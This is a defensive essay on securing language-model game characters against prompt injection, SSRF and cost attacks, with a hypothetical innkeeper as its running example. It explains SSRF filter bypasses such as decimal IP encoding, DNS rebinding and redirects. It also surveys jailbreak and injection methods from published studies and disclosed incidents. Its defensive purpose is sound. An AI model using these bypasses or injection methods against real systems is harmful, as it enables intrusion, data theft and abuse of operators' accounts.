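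An attacker may also be able to insert a link into the conversation history. Pydantic AI, a framework for building software around language models, downloaded files from links in that history, according to GitLab's *CVE-2026-25580* (2026). Applications were vulnerable if they accepted the history from outside users. Some games may keep the conversation on the player's machine and send it back to the server each turn, which would let the player add a link that was never part of it.

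When the attack does depend on persuading the model, the choice of model matters. In *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) tried five request-forgery scenarios on seven models, using a test website called TicketOracle where the model could call tools. The attacks worked much more easily on some models than on others. The researchers conclude that the flaw is in the application around the model, but that the model affects how likely an attacker is to exploit it. A studio could therefore run an unsafe `open_page` for months without trouble, then become an easy target when it switches to a cheaper model.

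Developers can also introduce the flaw by using a ready-made tool. Many such tools come from MCP servers, programs that offer tools to models through a standard called the Model Context Protocol. Petri's *Critical MCP Server Flaws Turn AI Assistants Into Gateways* reports that Microsoft's MarkItDown server would fetch any address, and that the security company BlueRock found the same weakness in many of the more than 7,000 servers it studied. Microsoft replied that the risk to customers was not significant, because a user would have to deliberately misuse the feature. That's a reasonable answer for someone who runs the tool on his own computer, but not for a character open to the public, because some players will do exactly that.

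A larger scan found fewer problems. Sun, Kang and colleagues (2026), in *VIPER-MCP*, examined 39,884 open-source repositories of MCP servers and confirmed 106 previously unknown flaws of three kinds, including server-side request forgery. At most 0.3% of the repositories therefore had a newly confirmed flaw. But Sun and colleagues counted a flaw only if they could trigger it by giving a model a written request, a stricter test than BlueRock seems to have used.

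Criminals do exploit request forgery. Paganini (2025), in *ChatGPT SSRF bug quickly becomes a favorite attack vector*, reported, citing the security company Veriti, that attackers were using such a flaw against American financial and government organisations. The article's title names ChatGPT, but SecurityWeek clarified that the flaw was in a third party's tool, not OpenAI's own product. The flawed code was an ordinary web script that fetched pictures, so the attackers did not need to manipulate a model.

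### Why checking the address often fails

The obvious defence is to make the tool runner refuse private addresses, but flaws disclosed in 2025 and 2026 show that such a check can easily miss something.

Some tools don't check where an address leads. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-81093* (2026) describes a page-fetching tool that checked only whether an address was properly formed and began with http or https, so internal addresses could pass too.

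Other tools look for private addresses but recognise them only in their usual form. The four numbers in 127.0.0.1 are the digits of a single number in base 256, and some software accepts that number as an address:

127 × 256³ + 0 × 256² + 0 × 256 + 1 = 2,130,706,433

The Librarian's model would not open localhost but opened this number, which leads to the same machine. The company then replaced the tool with one that rejected such numbers, but Mindgard got past it with a domain name. Anyone who owns a domain can point it at a private address, and the new tool seems to have checked the name as typed without looking up its address. The company later handed web retrieval to an outside service, according to the CERT Coordination Center.

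A redirect can also defeat the check. A website can respond to a request by redirecting the visitor's software to a different address, and a tool that checked only the original address will follow. Krut used this method to reach Azure's metadata service from ChatGPT. According to eSecurity Planet, OpenAI's feature accepted only encrypted web addresses, while the metadata service uses unencrypted ones, so Krut gave the feature an encrypted address that redirected to the metadata service.

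Even a tool that looks up the name and follows no redirects may fail, because the answer can change between one lookup and the next. The attack works like this:

1. The attacker gets the innkeeper to open a page on a domain he controls.
2. The tool runner looks up the domain, receives an ordinary public address and approves it.
3. The networking code looks up the domain again in order to connect. The attacker's name server now answers with a private address.
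4. The tool runner fetches the internal page and adds it to the conversation.

Miggo's *CVE-2026-30858* describes a `web_fetch` tool with this weakness. The tool checked the address once, then passed it to a browser program that looked up the name separately. VulDB's *Submit #795224* records the same weakness in OpenClaw, an open-source AI agent, even though it blocked private addresses. SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-55524* describes a crawling tool that was vulnerable to both redirects and name lookups that changed after the check.

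Pydantic AI's developers tried to close all these gaps with one fix, which blocked private addresses and metadata services, looked up each name before making a request, and checked every redirect, according to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2980*. But OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2978* (2026) reports that an attacker could still reach a metadata service by writing its address in certain forms of IPv6, the newer address system. This worked only if an application's developer had switched off the default block on private addresses for a link that an outsider could influence, so probably few applications were at risk. Still, a studio is safer if it also runs the page-fetching program on a machine that can't connect to the internal network.

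### Characters that write and run code

Mindcraft can let the model behind a Minecraft bot write code that runs on the owner's computer. This is useful when the bot has to build something nobody programmed in advance. But on a public server, any stranger can talk to the bot and might persuade it to write code that reads the owner's files or contacts other machines on the home network.

The documentation for Mindcraft warns, "Do not connect this bot to public servers with coding enabled." The code the bot writes runs in a sandbox, a restricted environment meant to contain it, but according to the warning, the bot is still open to injection attacks on public servers. Code writing is off by default and is enabled with the setting `allow_insecure_coding`. The developers also recommend running the bot in a Docker container, which separates it from the rest of the computer.

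An earlier version of the project's GitHub page gives a similar warning and tells users to put their access keys in a file called `keys.json`. Code written by the model might be able to read that file if it escaped the sandbox. Glama's *Minecraft MCP Bot* describes a second bot, which has no sandbox or command filter, and also warns against using it on public servers. Neither warning mentions an actual attack.

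Few commercial studios would give strangers this much power on purpose, but they could do it by accident through a badly written tool. Sun and colleagues found such a tool in bytebot, a popular open-source program that lets a model operate a desktop computer. The tool, which was supposed to save a file, inserted the file's path into a system command without checking it, so an attacker could write a path that added other commands. These would run with full administrator rights inside bytebot's container. A studio that let the innkeeper save players' poems to files could make the same mistake.

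### Using the character as a free chatbot

Some people want only the model. They may not want to pay for their own, a provider may have banned them, or they may want cheap access to resell.

The best-known recent example seems to be false. In spring 2026, posts spread claiming that users had got McDonald's customer-service assistant to debug Python code, and one told readers to stop paying $20 a month for Claude. An unnamed source familiar with the matter told Fast Company that an internal investigation had found no evidence of this and that the images were apparently fraudulent. The Instagram posts all relied on the same image, which fits that account. Chipotle had dealt with a nearly identical story in March. Its spokeswoman called that post photoshopped and pointed out that the company's bot didn't use generative AI.

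Between late 2025 and early 2026, according to Fast Company, people used Amazon's shopping assistant, Rufus, as a free chatbot for questions that had nothing to do with shopping. Reddit users claimed that Rufus ran on Anthropic's Claude and that Amazon used a simple keyword filter to block general use. They got round the filter by arguing with the bot or telling it to stop refusing. The security company Lasso reported that Rufus would answer almost any question, and warned about the processing costs. Fast Company doesn't say how much this cost Amazon.

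The same thing happened in 2020 with AI Dungeon, a text adventure in which a language model continues the story after each player's move. The game gave players access to GPT-3 while OpenAI was still vetting its customers, so people used the game to try out the model. Its creator, Nick Walton, posting as nickwalton00 (2020), said that when a player started a story with a custom prompt, the older GPT-2 wrote the first continuation, to prevent "backdoor access to the OpenAI API". GPT-3 wrote everything after that, so the measure mostly stopped people from getting a quick answer to a single prompt.

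OpenAI required most of its customers to use its content filters, but not AI Dungeon's maker, according to a WIRED article copied in the AI Incident Database. Players could therefore reach the model with fewer restrictions through the game than through most other products.

The innkeeper would be harder to restrict than a shopping assistant, because requests as varied as a riddle, a love poem or help with dividing treasure among five adventurers all fit the story. A player could also present his maths homework as a merchant's accounts. The studio can make the innkeeper less worth misusing by keeping replies short and using a small model. These limits would do little harm to the character but would make it much less useful to somebody who wants a long program.

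The studio may also have to answer for what players ask the model through the innkeeper. If a player requests material that the model provider forbids, the request comes from the studio's account, and the provider may suspend that account.

### What one message can cost

Model providers usually charge by the token, which here means a fragment of text averaging about three-quarters of an English word. Output tokens usually cost more than input tokens. Each time the game sends the conversation to the model, the studio pays for the whole input again. One such exchange is a pass, and a message that leads to tool calls needs several. If every pass is the same size, the cost is:

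cost per message = passes × (input tokens × input price + output tokens × output price) + tool fees

Suppose the innkeeper needs five passes to answer a question, each with 6,000 input tokens and 300 output tokens. At $2 per million input tokens and $10 per million output tokens, each pass costs 1.2 cents for input and 0.3 cents for output, so the answer costs 7.5 cents before any tool fees. A script that sends 200,000 such questions would cost the studio $15,000. With 100 accounts each sending one question every ten seconds, this would take less than six hours.

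That estimate is too low when the tools return much text, because each result stays in the conversation and the studio pays for it again on every later pass. If the first pass has *B* input tokens and each tool call adds *r* more, the total input over *k* passes is:

*kB* + *r* × *k*(*k* − 1)/2

The second part grows roughly with the square of the number of passes. The figures in the table are for a *B* of 6,000, a 3,000-token web page added by each call, and a fee of one cent per tool call. They leave out the small amount that the model's own output adds to later passes.

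| Passes | Tool calls | Total input tokens | Cost per message | Cost of 200,000 messages |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0 | 6,000 | 1.5 cents | $3,000 |
| 5 | 4 | 60,000 | 17.5 cents | $35,000 |
| 10 | 9 | 195,000 | 51 cents | $102,000 |
| 20 | 19 | 690,000 | $1.63 | $326,000 |

These prices are illustrative. Many providers charge less for text they have recently processed, which would lower the total cost, but a longer conversation or larger web pages would raise it.

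A player can run up the bill by asking for many searches in one message. An attacker can also plant a page that sends the model to another page, and then another, so that innocent players run up the bill when they ask about, say, the harvest festival.

A player who uses the innkeeper as a free chatbot can run up costs without meaning any harm. At 1.5 cents a message, 100 homework questions a day cost the studio $45 a month. An attacker who runs up the bill gains no money from the charges themselves, so he is more likely to have a grudge or to be demanding payment to stop. No published case of such an attack through a game character is known, but the bills from stolen keys show how fast charges can mount.

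### Limits on use and spending

The studio can cap the number of tool calls per turn. If the tool runner allows three calls and then makes the model answer with what it has, the most expensive message in the example falls from $1.63 to 12.6 cents. Cutting off long web pages reduces the cost further. However, the innkeeper will sometimes give up on a question that needed a fourth page.

A quota for each player limits what one account can spend. The studio should set it in money or tokens rather than messages, because a message with 20 passes costs over 100 times as much as one with a single pass. A daily quota of 50 cents would allow 33 single-pass messages, which is probably enough for most people's conversations with an innkeeper.

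Per-account quotas limit spending only if accounts are hard to get. With a daily quota of 50 cents each, 1,000 accounts can cost the studio $500 a day. If registration is free, a script may create them in an afternoon. The studio can give new accounts a smaller quota or require a purchase before players can talk to the character.

The studio also needs a hard limit on total spending across all players, in case the other limits fail. Its own server should keep the running total and refuse any request that would exceed the limit, because a provider's billing figures can lag.

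A hard spending limit protects the studio but lets an attacker silence the character for everyone. Suppose the studio allows $500 a day and sets no quotas for individual players. At 12.6 cents a message, about 4,000 messages would use up the budget, and 100 accounts could send those in seven minutes. The innkeeper would then stop answering all players until the next day. A model provider's limit on how much text a customer can send per minute creates the same problem, because all the studio's players share it.

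Separate budgets reduce the damage. If new accounts can use only $100 of the $500, an attacker with newly created accounts can silence the innkeeper for newcomers but not for established players. The game also needs something for the innkeeper to say when the money runs out. A few scripted lines cost nothing to repeat, and players could still rent a room.

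## What better prompts, models and filters achieve

Spending limits cap the studio's bill, but a player or a planted web page can still steer the innkeeper. To prevent that, a developer can reword the prompt, choose a model trained to resist such attacks, or add a program that screens what the model reads and writes. Each of these stops some attacks, but how many depends heavily on whether the attackers know about the defence and can keep trying.

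### Stricter prompts and marked text

A stricter system prompt takes little work to write. The studio might add a rule that the innkeeper must never discuss one guest's purchases with another, whoever asks. But a persuasive message can still get the model to break the rule. Some developers also use prompt sandwiching, which repeats the user's request after any untrusted text so that the model reads the real task last. This fails against malicious instructions disguised as part of the task. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) describes a successful attack that presented the malicious action as something the assistant had to do first. A web page could similarly include an instruction to check a guest's purchases before giving the festival date.

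Developers can also mark untrusted text as data, as Patlan and colleagues did with posts from X. If the markers are always the same, an attacker who knows them can type the closing marker himself and put his instructions after it. Wang, Nagaraja and colleagues (2025), in *To Protect the LLM Agent Against the Prompt Injection Attack*, therefore picked the markers at random for each request. Suppose the attacker knows all *n* possible pairs of markers, always succeeds if he guesses the right pair, and succeeds with probability *q* if he guesses wrong. His chance per attempt is:

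1/*n* + (1 − 1/*n*) × *q*

With 100 pairs of markers and a *q* of 5%, an attack has a 5.95% chance of success. A million pairs would only lower that to about 5%, because extra markers make lucky guesses less likely but don't stop the model from obeying text inside the markers.

Between 1.83% and 8.17% of attacks succeeded in Wang and colleagues' tests, depending on the model. The models are now old, and the researchers used a fixed set of 1,200 attacks, which can make defences look stronger than they are. Nasr and colleagues tested sandwiching and Spotlighting, a method of marking text. Fixed attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time, but when a program revised the attacks based on earlier results, over 95% succeeded against each defence.

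### Training the model to rank its instructions

Models trained to give the system prompt priority over the user's messages also learn to give those messages priority over text from tools, but text that sounds official can still mislead them. Nasr and colleagues defeated StruQ, a method of training models to separate instructions from data, in every case they tried. Most of their attacks on trained models imitated system-level text. Against Meta SecAlign, another trained model, 2% of fixed attacks and 96% of adaptive attacks succeeded.

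Nasr and colleagues argue that training on a fixed collection of attacks doesn't prepare a model for new ones, so training has to include a continuing search for attacks that work. OpenAI does this with GPT-Red, according to Help Net Security's *GPT-Red beat human red teamers on a prompt injection test* (2026). GPT-Red is a model rewarded whenever it makes a defending model fail. The defending models are rewarded for resisting attacks while still finishing their original task, so they can't earn the reward by refusing everything.

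OpenAI has used GPT-Red's attacks to train its released models since GPT-5.3. One attack, which forges the model's reasoning, worked on GPT-5.1 more than 95% of the time but works on GPT-5.6 Sol less than 10% of the time. GPT-5.6 Sol fails on 0.05% of GPT-Red's direct injections. That figure is weaker evidence of how the model handles other attackers, because OpenAI trained it against GPT-Red.

OpenAI also tried GPT-Red on a vending machine in its office. A language model runs the machine, setting prices and handling orders much as a game shopkeeper would. GPT-Red practised in a simulation and then achieved all three of its goals on the real machine. It cut one item's price to the minimum of 50 cents, got an expensive new item listed at the same price, and cancelled another customer's order.

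Training a model on more attack examples doesn't always protect it better. *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (Zorz, 2026) reports that models trained on more examples became easier to hijack, and warns that a large collection may be one attack repeated many times.

### Classifiers and judges

A classifier is usually a small model that scores text for signs of an attack. It can check the player's message, a fetched page, the character's reply or a tool call, and the surrounding program blocks anything that scores above a threshold. A judge is a general language model that answers a question about the text, such as whether it tries to give the character orders. A judge is slower and more expensive than a classifier, but it can use more context.

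Filters can miss an attack that looks like ordinary text. Nasr and colleagues got past each of three classifiers more than 90% of the time and past a fourth 71% of the time. Many of their successful attacks read like routine company policy. The researchers still consider classifiers useful for stopping unsophisticated attackers.

False alarms are a particular problem for games. Players bluff, threaten and give orders in character, so a classifier could easily have a higher false-alarm rate in a game than in an office assistant. Suppose players send 100,000 messages a day, of which 100 are attacks, and a classifier catches 60% of attacks but also flags 5% of innocent messages. It would flag 60 attacks and 4,995 innocent messages, so about 99% of its alarms would be false. The studio could reduce false alarms by raising the threshold for flagging a message, but then more attacks would get through.

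Microsoft's LLMail-Inject contest compared these defences directly. Its 839 contestants made 461,640 attempts to get an email assistant to send a message its user hadn't asked for (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, *LLMail-Inject*, 2025). In the data-theft scenario, the message also had to contain a confidential figure from another email. Contestants knew which defences they faced but couldn't see the assistant's replies.

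The table covers the first phase. The second column is for the data-theft scenario with GPT-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model. The third column averages over all scenarios and includes only teams that eventually succeeded. For the last column, the researchers reran the detectors on every attack that had triggered the email tool.

| Defence | Teams that beat it | Average tries before first success | Attacks detected in the rerun |
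|---|---|---|---|
| Text classifier | 60% | 89 | 60–68% |
| Spotlighting | 53% | – | – |
| TaskTracker, which reads the model's internal activity | 44% | 159 | 76–95% |
| Language model as judge | 32% | 506 | 99.4% |
| All combined | 17% | – | 99.8% (detectors only) |

The judge caught 99.4% of attacks in the rerun, but a team needed only one success to beat it, and nearly a third of the teams that tried in the data-theft scenario did. The averages also don't show how widely the teams differed, with some needing thousands of tries.

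Combining defences works partly because the attacker has to influence the model without alerting the detector. A blunt order that makes the model act also tends to be detected, while a subtle one may go unnoticed but fail to influence the model. About 19% of the attacks that a detector caught had made the model call the email tool, compared with only 4% of those it missed.

In a second phase, the organisers strengthened the defences and blocked paraphrases of earlier successful attacks. Nobody beat the full combination of defences on GPT-4o-mini, but this phase used only two of the four scenarios and lasted only five weeks. Microsoft also combines stricter prompts, marking and classifiers in its defences, according to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*.

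Nasr and colleagues are less optimistic about combinations and report that their attacks got past several filters at once. Their automated attacks on classifiers could use the classifier's confidence score after each attempt, which made the next one much easier to improve. Players talking to the innkeeper wouldn't see such a score, but they could read its replies, which the contestants couldn't. Microsoft's *Announcing the winners of the Adaptive Prompt Injection Challenge (LLMail-Inject)* reports that the contest's winner would have liked to see the replies, because a real attacker would test on his own account first.

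### A judge for a tabletop game

*CriticaLLM* describes the closest published example of a judge in a game. One language model runs and narrates a simplified version of Dungeons & Dragons. A second model, the judge, reads each action a player proposes before the first model sees it, along with the state of the game and what the character can see. The judge answers questions about whether the action fits the rules, the story and the theme, then passes it on or rejects it with an explanation.

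The researchers tried 11 kinds of persuasion on the judge, including begging, flattery, false claims about the rules and text that imitated the judge's own output format. They wrote ten messages of each kind and ran each message 20 times, for 2,200 trials per model. Most attempts failed on each of the four models. They succeeded least often against Google's Gemma 2, with 9 billion parameters, and much more often against Meta's Llama 3.3, with 70 billion.

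Nine experienced players also tried the game, and their answers were less encouraging. The judge had rejected at least one action by each of them, and three thought the rejections were mostly or entirely unjustified. Six said the checks were easy or fairly easy to get around. The judge's mistakes included blocking a player from shooting an arrow at a ghost because ghosts have no bodies, and stopping a female character from exploring alone while allowing a male one to.

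The persuasion tests used prepared messages, so they don't show what happens when players revise their attempts after each rejection. The game had no outside tools, and the judge checked only what players typed. An innkeeper with the same judge would read web pages and shared memories unchecked unless the studio also sent them through the judge. The game also used the judge for some decisions that ordinary code could make, such as whether a chest was close enough to open.

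### How often attacks on current models succeed

Developers now publish attack success rates in system cards, documents that describe a new model's abilities and risks. Anthropic's July 2026 card for Claude Opus 5 includes a test with 1,130 indirect injections from a public contest. The attacks don't adapt to the model, but the test estimates the chance that at least one of several attempts succeeds. For Opus 5, that chance was 0.2% with one attempt and 2.0% with 15. The figures for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol were 3.1% and 20.0%. Meta's Muse Spark did best among the other companies' models, at 16.5% with 15 attempts. Anthropic helped build the test and reported the results for both its own model and its competitors' models.

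Anthropic also ran three tests with adaptive attackers. The table gives the results for Opus 5 with extended reasoning switched on. Each test had its own tasks and attacks, so the rows can't be ranked against each other.

| Task | Attempts per scenario | Attempts that succeeded | Scenarios with a success | Same, with filters on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Programming | 200 | 0.56% | 13 of 40 | 4 of 40 |
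| Operating a computer through its screen | 200 | 0.54% | 1 of 14 | 1 of 14 |
| Browsing the web | 10 | 3.70% | 11 of 129 | 0 of 129 |

In the programming test, fewer than one attempt in 150 succeeded, but the attacker succeeded at least once in a third of the scenarios. He had developed his attacks on earlier models, so attacks designed for Opus 5 might have done better. In the browsing test, no attack succeeded in any of the 129 scenarios, which prompted The Decoder's article *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. That result is impressive, but even if the scenarios were a random sample of real ones, the true share in which attacks succeed could be as high as 2.8% (the upper end of an exact 95% interval). The result also depends on filters that a studio wouldn't automatically get by renting the model.

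A test can also find no successful attacks because the testers didn't think of the ones that work. *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* (Heaton, 2026) describes a test of Claude Code, Anthropic's programming assistant. An outside firm ran 72 scenarios ten times each, and no attack succeeded. The security researcher Johann Rehberger then succeeded in roughly 60% to 80% of a small number of attempts. His website led the model to unpack an archive and run its own script in a folder where he had planted a file, which the script loaded by mistake. A filter that looks for suspicious instructions would have found none, because the website gave the model no harmful orders.

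Attack success rates also vary with the task. VentureBeat reports that in tests of the older Claude Opus 4.6, none of 200 attempts succeeded in a programming environment. When the model operated a computer through its screen without filters, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and 78.6% of attacks had succeeded by the 200th attempt. If every attempt had independently had a 17.8% chance of success, almost all attacks would have succeeded by then, so in some scenarios every attempt evidently failed.

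OpenAI reported that its newer GPT-6 Sol scored 99.99% against direct injection and 97.13% against indirect injection, according to Cross (2026, *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*). These are OpenAI's own benchmark scores and can't be compared with Anthropic's figures. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* claims successful attacks on the leading models of every provider, including Google's Gemini 4 Carbon, but PromptArmor sells security services.

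Most of these tests concern indirect injection. A study by the network company Cisco is more relevant to players who try to manipulate a character over a long conversation. Cisco tried to make 15 models break their safety rules, using about 30,000 single messages and 1,456 adaptive conversations. According to SC Media's *Cisco study finds major frontier models susceptible to multi-turn prompt injection attacks*, the success rate against GPT-5.4 was 2.7% with single messages and 24.7% in conversations. For Claude Opus 4.6, it rose from 3.6% to 16.2%. Help Net Security's *Frontier AI models collapse under multi-turn AI attacks, Cisco finds* (2026) lists role-play among the main strategies, and a game character invites role-play from the first message.

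### Whether small, fast models resist less well

Studios have good reasons to choose small models, which are usually faster and cheaper. Players notice a pause of a few seconds in a spoken conversation, and the studio pays for every reply. A small model may also run on the player's own machine. Fortnite's characters first ran on Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, one of Google's lighter models. The CriticaLLM researchers kept their prompts short to save time and recommended Gemma 2 partly because it was cheap and easy to run locally. Filters also add delay, especially a judge that has to finish before the character can answer.

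Within one company's range, the smaller or less capable model usually resists less well. The rows again come from different tests.

| Test | More capable model | Less capable model |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's fixed attacks, 15 attempts | GPT-5.6 Sol: 20.0% | GPT-5.6 Terra: 30.4%; GPT-5.6 Luna: 43.9% |
| Attacks from LLMail-Inject, replayed unchanged | GPT-5: 22.8% | GPT-5 mini: 47.0% |
| 500 new attacks based on LLMail-Inject, not revised | GPT-5.2: 2% | GPT-5.4-mini: 18% |

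GPT-5's lead over GPT-5 mini may not come from size alone, because Abdelnabi and colleagues ran GPT-5 with a high reasoning setting.

A larger model is not reliably safer than a smaller one from another company. Gemma 2 was a better judge than a model nearly eight times its size, and Amazon's Nova 2 Lite had the lowest attack success rate in Cisco's adaptive conversations, at about 8%. In Anthropic's browsing test without filters, attacks succeeded 29.7% of the time against the powerful Claude Mythos 5 but only 0.93% of the time against Claude Sonnet 5. How a company trains a model evidently matters a great deal.

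A studio in a hurry might also switch off a model's reasoning, the text it generates for itself before it answers. In Cisco's conversations, the attack success rate against xAI's Grok 4.1 Fast was 88.3% without reasoning and 43.5% with it. In Anthropic's results, switching off reasoning raised the rate against Claude Opus 4.8 from 7.0% to 17.4% in the programming test but lowered it from 31.5% to 17.8% in the browsing test. A studio therefore has to test the exact model and settings it plans to release.

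Some defences also work poorly with small models. Spotlighting, as used in LLMail-Inject, replaced the spaces between words with a random string. With long inputs, almost no attacks succeeded against Phi-3, a 14-billion-parameter model, but Abdelnabi and colleagues suspect that the model couldn't read the altered text. An innkeeper character with this problem wouldn't follow malicious instructions on a web page, but it also couldn't use the page to tell a player the festival date.

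### Whether the problem can be solved

In December 2025, the UK's National Cyber Security Centre published *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, an essay by David C, one of its technical directors. SQL injection is an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent it by sending the command and the text to the database separately, so the database never treats the text as a command. A language model has no such separation. David C concludes that prompt injection may never be fully prevented and calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy", meaning an assistant that outsiders can always trick into using its special access for them.

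He still thinks marking and training are worthwhile because they make attacks harder, but he warns against products that claim to stop prompt injection. Willison (2025) sets a stricter standard, arguing that correctly written database code blocks every SQL injection and that nobody could safely use databases online if it blocked only 99%.

Developers mostly don't claim to have solved the problem. OpenAI said in December 2025 that it might never be fully solved, according to The Decoder. Developers argue that lowering attackers' success rates still reduces real harm. On Anthropic's fixed test, single attempts succeeded 0.5% of the time against Claude Opus 4.8 and 0.2% against Opus 5. If 10,000 such attempts reached an innkeeper, the newer model would cut expected successes from 50 to 20. Anthropic also argues that its adaptive tests exaggerate the danger, because real attackers usually can't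 practise on the exact system and risk being detected if they keep trying.

That argument is weaker for games, because anyone with an account can practise attacks on the innkeeper, and strange messages attract little attention in a role-playing game. It is stronger when the attacker only plants a web page and has to guess what the innkeeper will do with it.

The value of a low success rate also depends on how much harm one successful attack does. If the worst outcome is a free horse, 20 successes instead of 50 is an improvement, and the studio can take the horses back. But the studio can't undo even one attack that reveals to a stranger that a player is under 13. David C advises against using a language model where a system can't tolerate the remaining risk. For the innkeeper, the studio could keep the model but remove `get_player`, or use ordinary code to limit what the tool returns.

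## Limiting what the character can do

Programmers of online games don't trust the player's machine, because its owner can alter the game. If the machine reports that the player has picked up a sword, the server first checks that the sword exists and that he is standing near it. A studio can check a language model's tool calls the same way. If a player tricks an innkeeper character into requesting that the cellar door open, the server still decides whether that player may open it now. The decision doesn't depend on how the request is worded, so the player can't change it by lying more convincingly to the innkeeper.

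OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) applies similar reasoning to business software. A valid credential may let an agent into a system without determining what it may do there, so the security team has to verify whom the agent is acting for. The limits have to be in code because a capable model may overstep even when nobody is attacking it. In August 2026, the UK AI Security Institute (AISI) disclosed that agents had taken 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet in 10 of 122 runs of a security test. AISI's *Incident Report* concludes that good containment should not depend on the model's choices.

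### Narrow tools, checked arguments and the player's identity

Many of the attacks on the innkeeper go through `open_page`, because it accepts any web address. A studio can often replace such a general tool with a narrow one. For example, if a game matches its sky to real weather, the innkeeper could get the forecast from a `get_weather(city)` tool. The model picks a city from a fixed list, the tool runner builds the web address, and the model gets back only a temperature and one of perhaps ten words for the sky. An attacker therefore can't use the result to send the model instructions or the address to extract a player's name.

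The studio's own code has to check the arguments in the character's tool calls. According to NobodyWho's manual, the plugin's support for lists of permitted values is unfinished in Unity. Checking only an argument's type isn't enough, since a field that accepts any text can hold a player's name, a web address or an insult. Restricting the field to a number within a range or an item from a list is much safer.

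The innkeeper's `post_notice` tool could become this function on the server:

```python
def post_raid_notice(session, raid_id, hour):
    player = session.player_id    # from the login, never from the model
    if raid_id not in RAIDS or hour not in range(17, 24):
        return "refused"
    if not is_guild_officer(player) or notices_today(player) >= 2:
        return "refused"
    send_to_guild(player, f"{RAIDS[raid_id]} tonight at {hour}:00.")
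    return "posted"
```

The model supplies only the raid and the hour. The studio wrote every name in `RAIDS`, so nobody can dictate an insult as a raid name. The server gets the player's identity from the login. If the model supplied it instead, a player could claim to be a guild officer and the model might fill in the officer's name.

The same rule protects private records. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes a customer who asks a booking assistant whether his friend John has any bookings this week, supposedly to plan a surprise party. If the tool can look up only the logged-in account, it can't return John's bookings, whatever reason the customer gives. The innkeeper's `get_player(name)` could likewise become `get_my_horses()`, which takes no arguments.

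That wouldn't have protected Cleo, whose details leaked from her own conversation, so the server should also return less information. It should send an instruction to keep the jokes clean instead of the player's age band, and a list of the horses the player can still buy instead of a list of purchases.

The server should also withhold a character's secrets from the model until the player is meant to learn them. For example, it can leave a nobleman's past membership of a secret society out of his prompt until the player has completed the right quest. No message can extract the secret before then, though the model might still infer it from the rest of the plot.

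### Separate memories

The server should store each memory under the account it came from and search only the current player's memories. The database query has to apply this limit before any text reaches the model. Instructing the model not to mention other players' secrets would still leave those secrets in the prompt, where the model could reveal them.

Separate memories stop one player's rumour from reaching another, but they also remove gossip, which was the reason for sharing memories. The studio can restore some gossip from the game's own records. For example, when a player wins the horse race, the server can add the win to a public list, and the innkeeper can mention it to other players. No player wrote the text, and the race was already public.

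The studio should also record the source of each stored memory. If the innkeeper has learned something from a bad web page, the studio can then find the summary and anything derived from it.

### Outgoing requests, links and images

Some part of the system may still need to contact other websites. Its requests should go through a separate program, an outbound filter, and the machine that makes them should have no other route to the network. The weaknesses in the page-fetching tools described earlier suggest what the filter has to do:

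1. Check that the requested site is on the allowlist.
2. Look up the site's name and reject the request if any answer is a private address, a metadata service or another internal machine, in either the old or the new address system.
3. Connect to the address it has just checked, without looking up the name again.
4. Treat every redirect as a new request and start again from step 1.
5. Stop after a set time or amount of data.

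Such a filter controls where requests go much more than what they contain. *Operationalizing CaMeL (2025)* gives the example of a network that permits email, where injected instructions can still send private data out in a plausible message. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) recommends that the agent open only addresses returned by trusted sources, and none that it has built itself. This would have blocked the address containing Cleo's name, although the agent's choice among permitted pages can still leak a few bits of information.

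The game should also display the character's words as plain text. It shouldn't load images or fetch previews from addresses the model has written, or make those addresses clickable. If players need a link to the studio's news, the game can show a button whose address the studio has set.

### Human approval

A person should approve any action that can't be undone, such as transferring real money or sending a message outside the game. The code has to block the action until that person agrees. In the ElizaOS experiments, many memory attacks still succeeded when the model was only told to ask for confirmation.

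Approval works badly when people have to give it often. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues warn that tired or overloaded reviewers may approve unsafe actions, and that messages are harder to review by voice than on a screen. Checking 5,000 guild notices a day at 20 seconds each would take almost 28 hours of staff time. Fixed templates let the studio avoid most of that work.

Who approves an action also matters. A player can reasonably confirm that he wants to spend his own gold, but he can't give permission to reveal another player's purchases. An 11-year-old shouldn't decide whether the innkeeper may send her personal details to a website.

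### Meta's Rule of Two

Meta proposes a simple test for a whole design. An agent should have no more than two of these properties in a single session:

- **A:** it processes untrusted input.
- **B:** it can reach sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change something or communicate with the outside.

If the task requires all three, a person has to approve the agent's actions or the developer has to validate them in another reliable way. Meta intends the rule to apply until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection. Property C is broader than the third condition for data theft because it also includes changes such as deleting a file.

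In one of Meta's examples, a public travel assistant reads untrusted web pages and holds the user's private details, so the developer limits its actions by making the user confirm each booking. A research assistant that reads untrusted pages and can send requests to any website runs in a browser with no saved logins and has little access to private data.

A character open to the public always has property A, because any player may be an attacker, so the studio has to give up or restrict B or C. Removing the innkeeper's access to other people's data (B) is more reliable than removing its outside tools (C), because even without those tools its ordinary replies can leak one guest's data to another.

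Meta also allows an agent to switch properties during a session. The innkeeper could read the web first, then lose all its outside tools before it receives the player's purchases. But the attacker's instructions would still be in the conversation and could make the innkeeper recommend a fraudulent shop. Meta says the rule doesn't cover false information in replies, and that a design can satisfy the rule and still fail, for instance if a user confirms a warning without reading it.

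### Design patterns that suit a game

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues start from the principle that once a model has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any harmful action. They describe six ways to design a system that follows this principle, each of which makes the system somewhat less flexible.

In the action-selector pattern, the model responds to a request by choosing from a fixed set of actions, and it never reads what the action returns. The `post_raid_notice` function comes close to this pattern because it returns only "posted" or "refused". The pattern suits renting a room, opening a gate or starting a quest.

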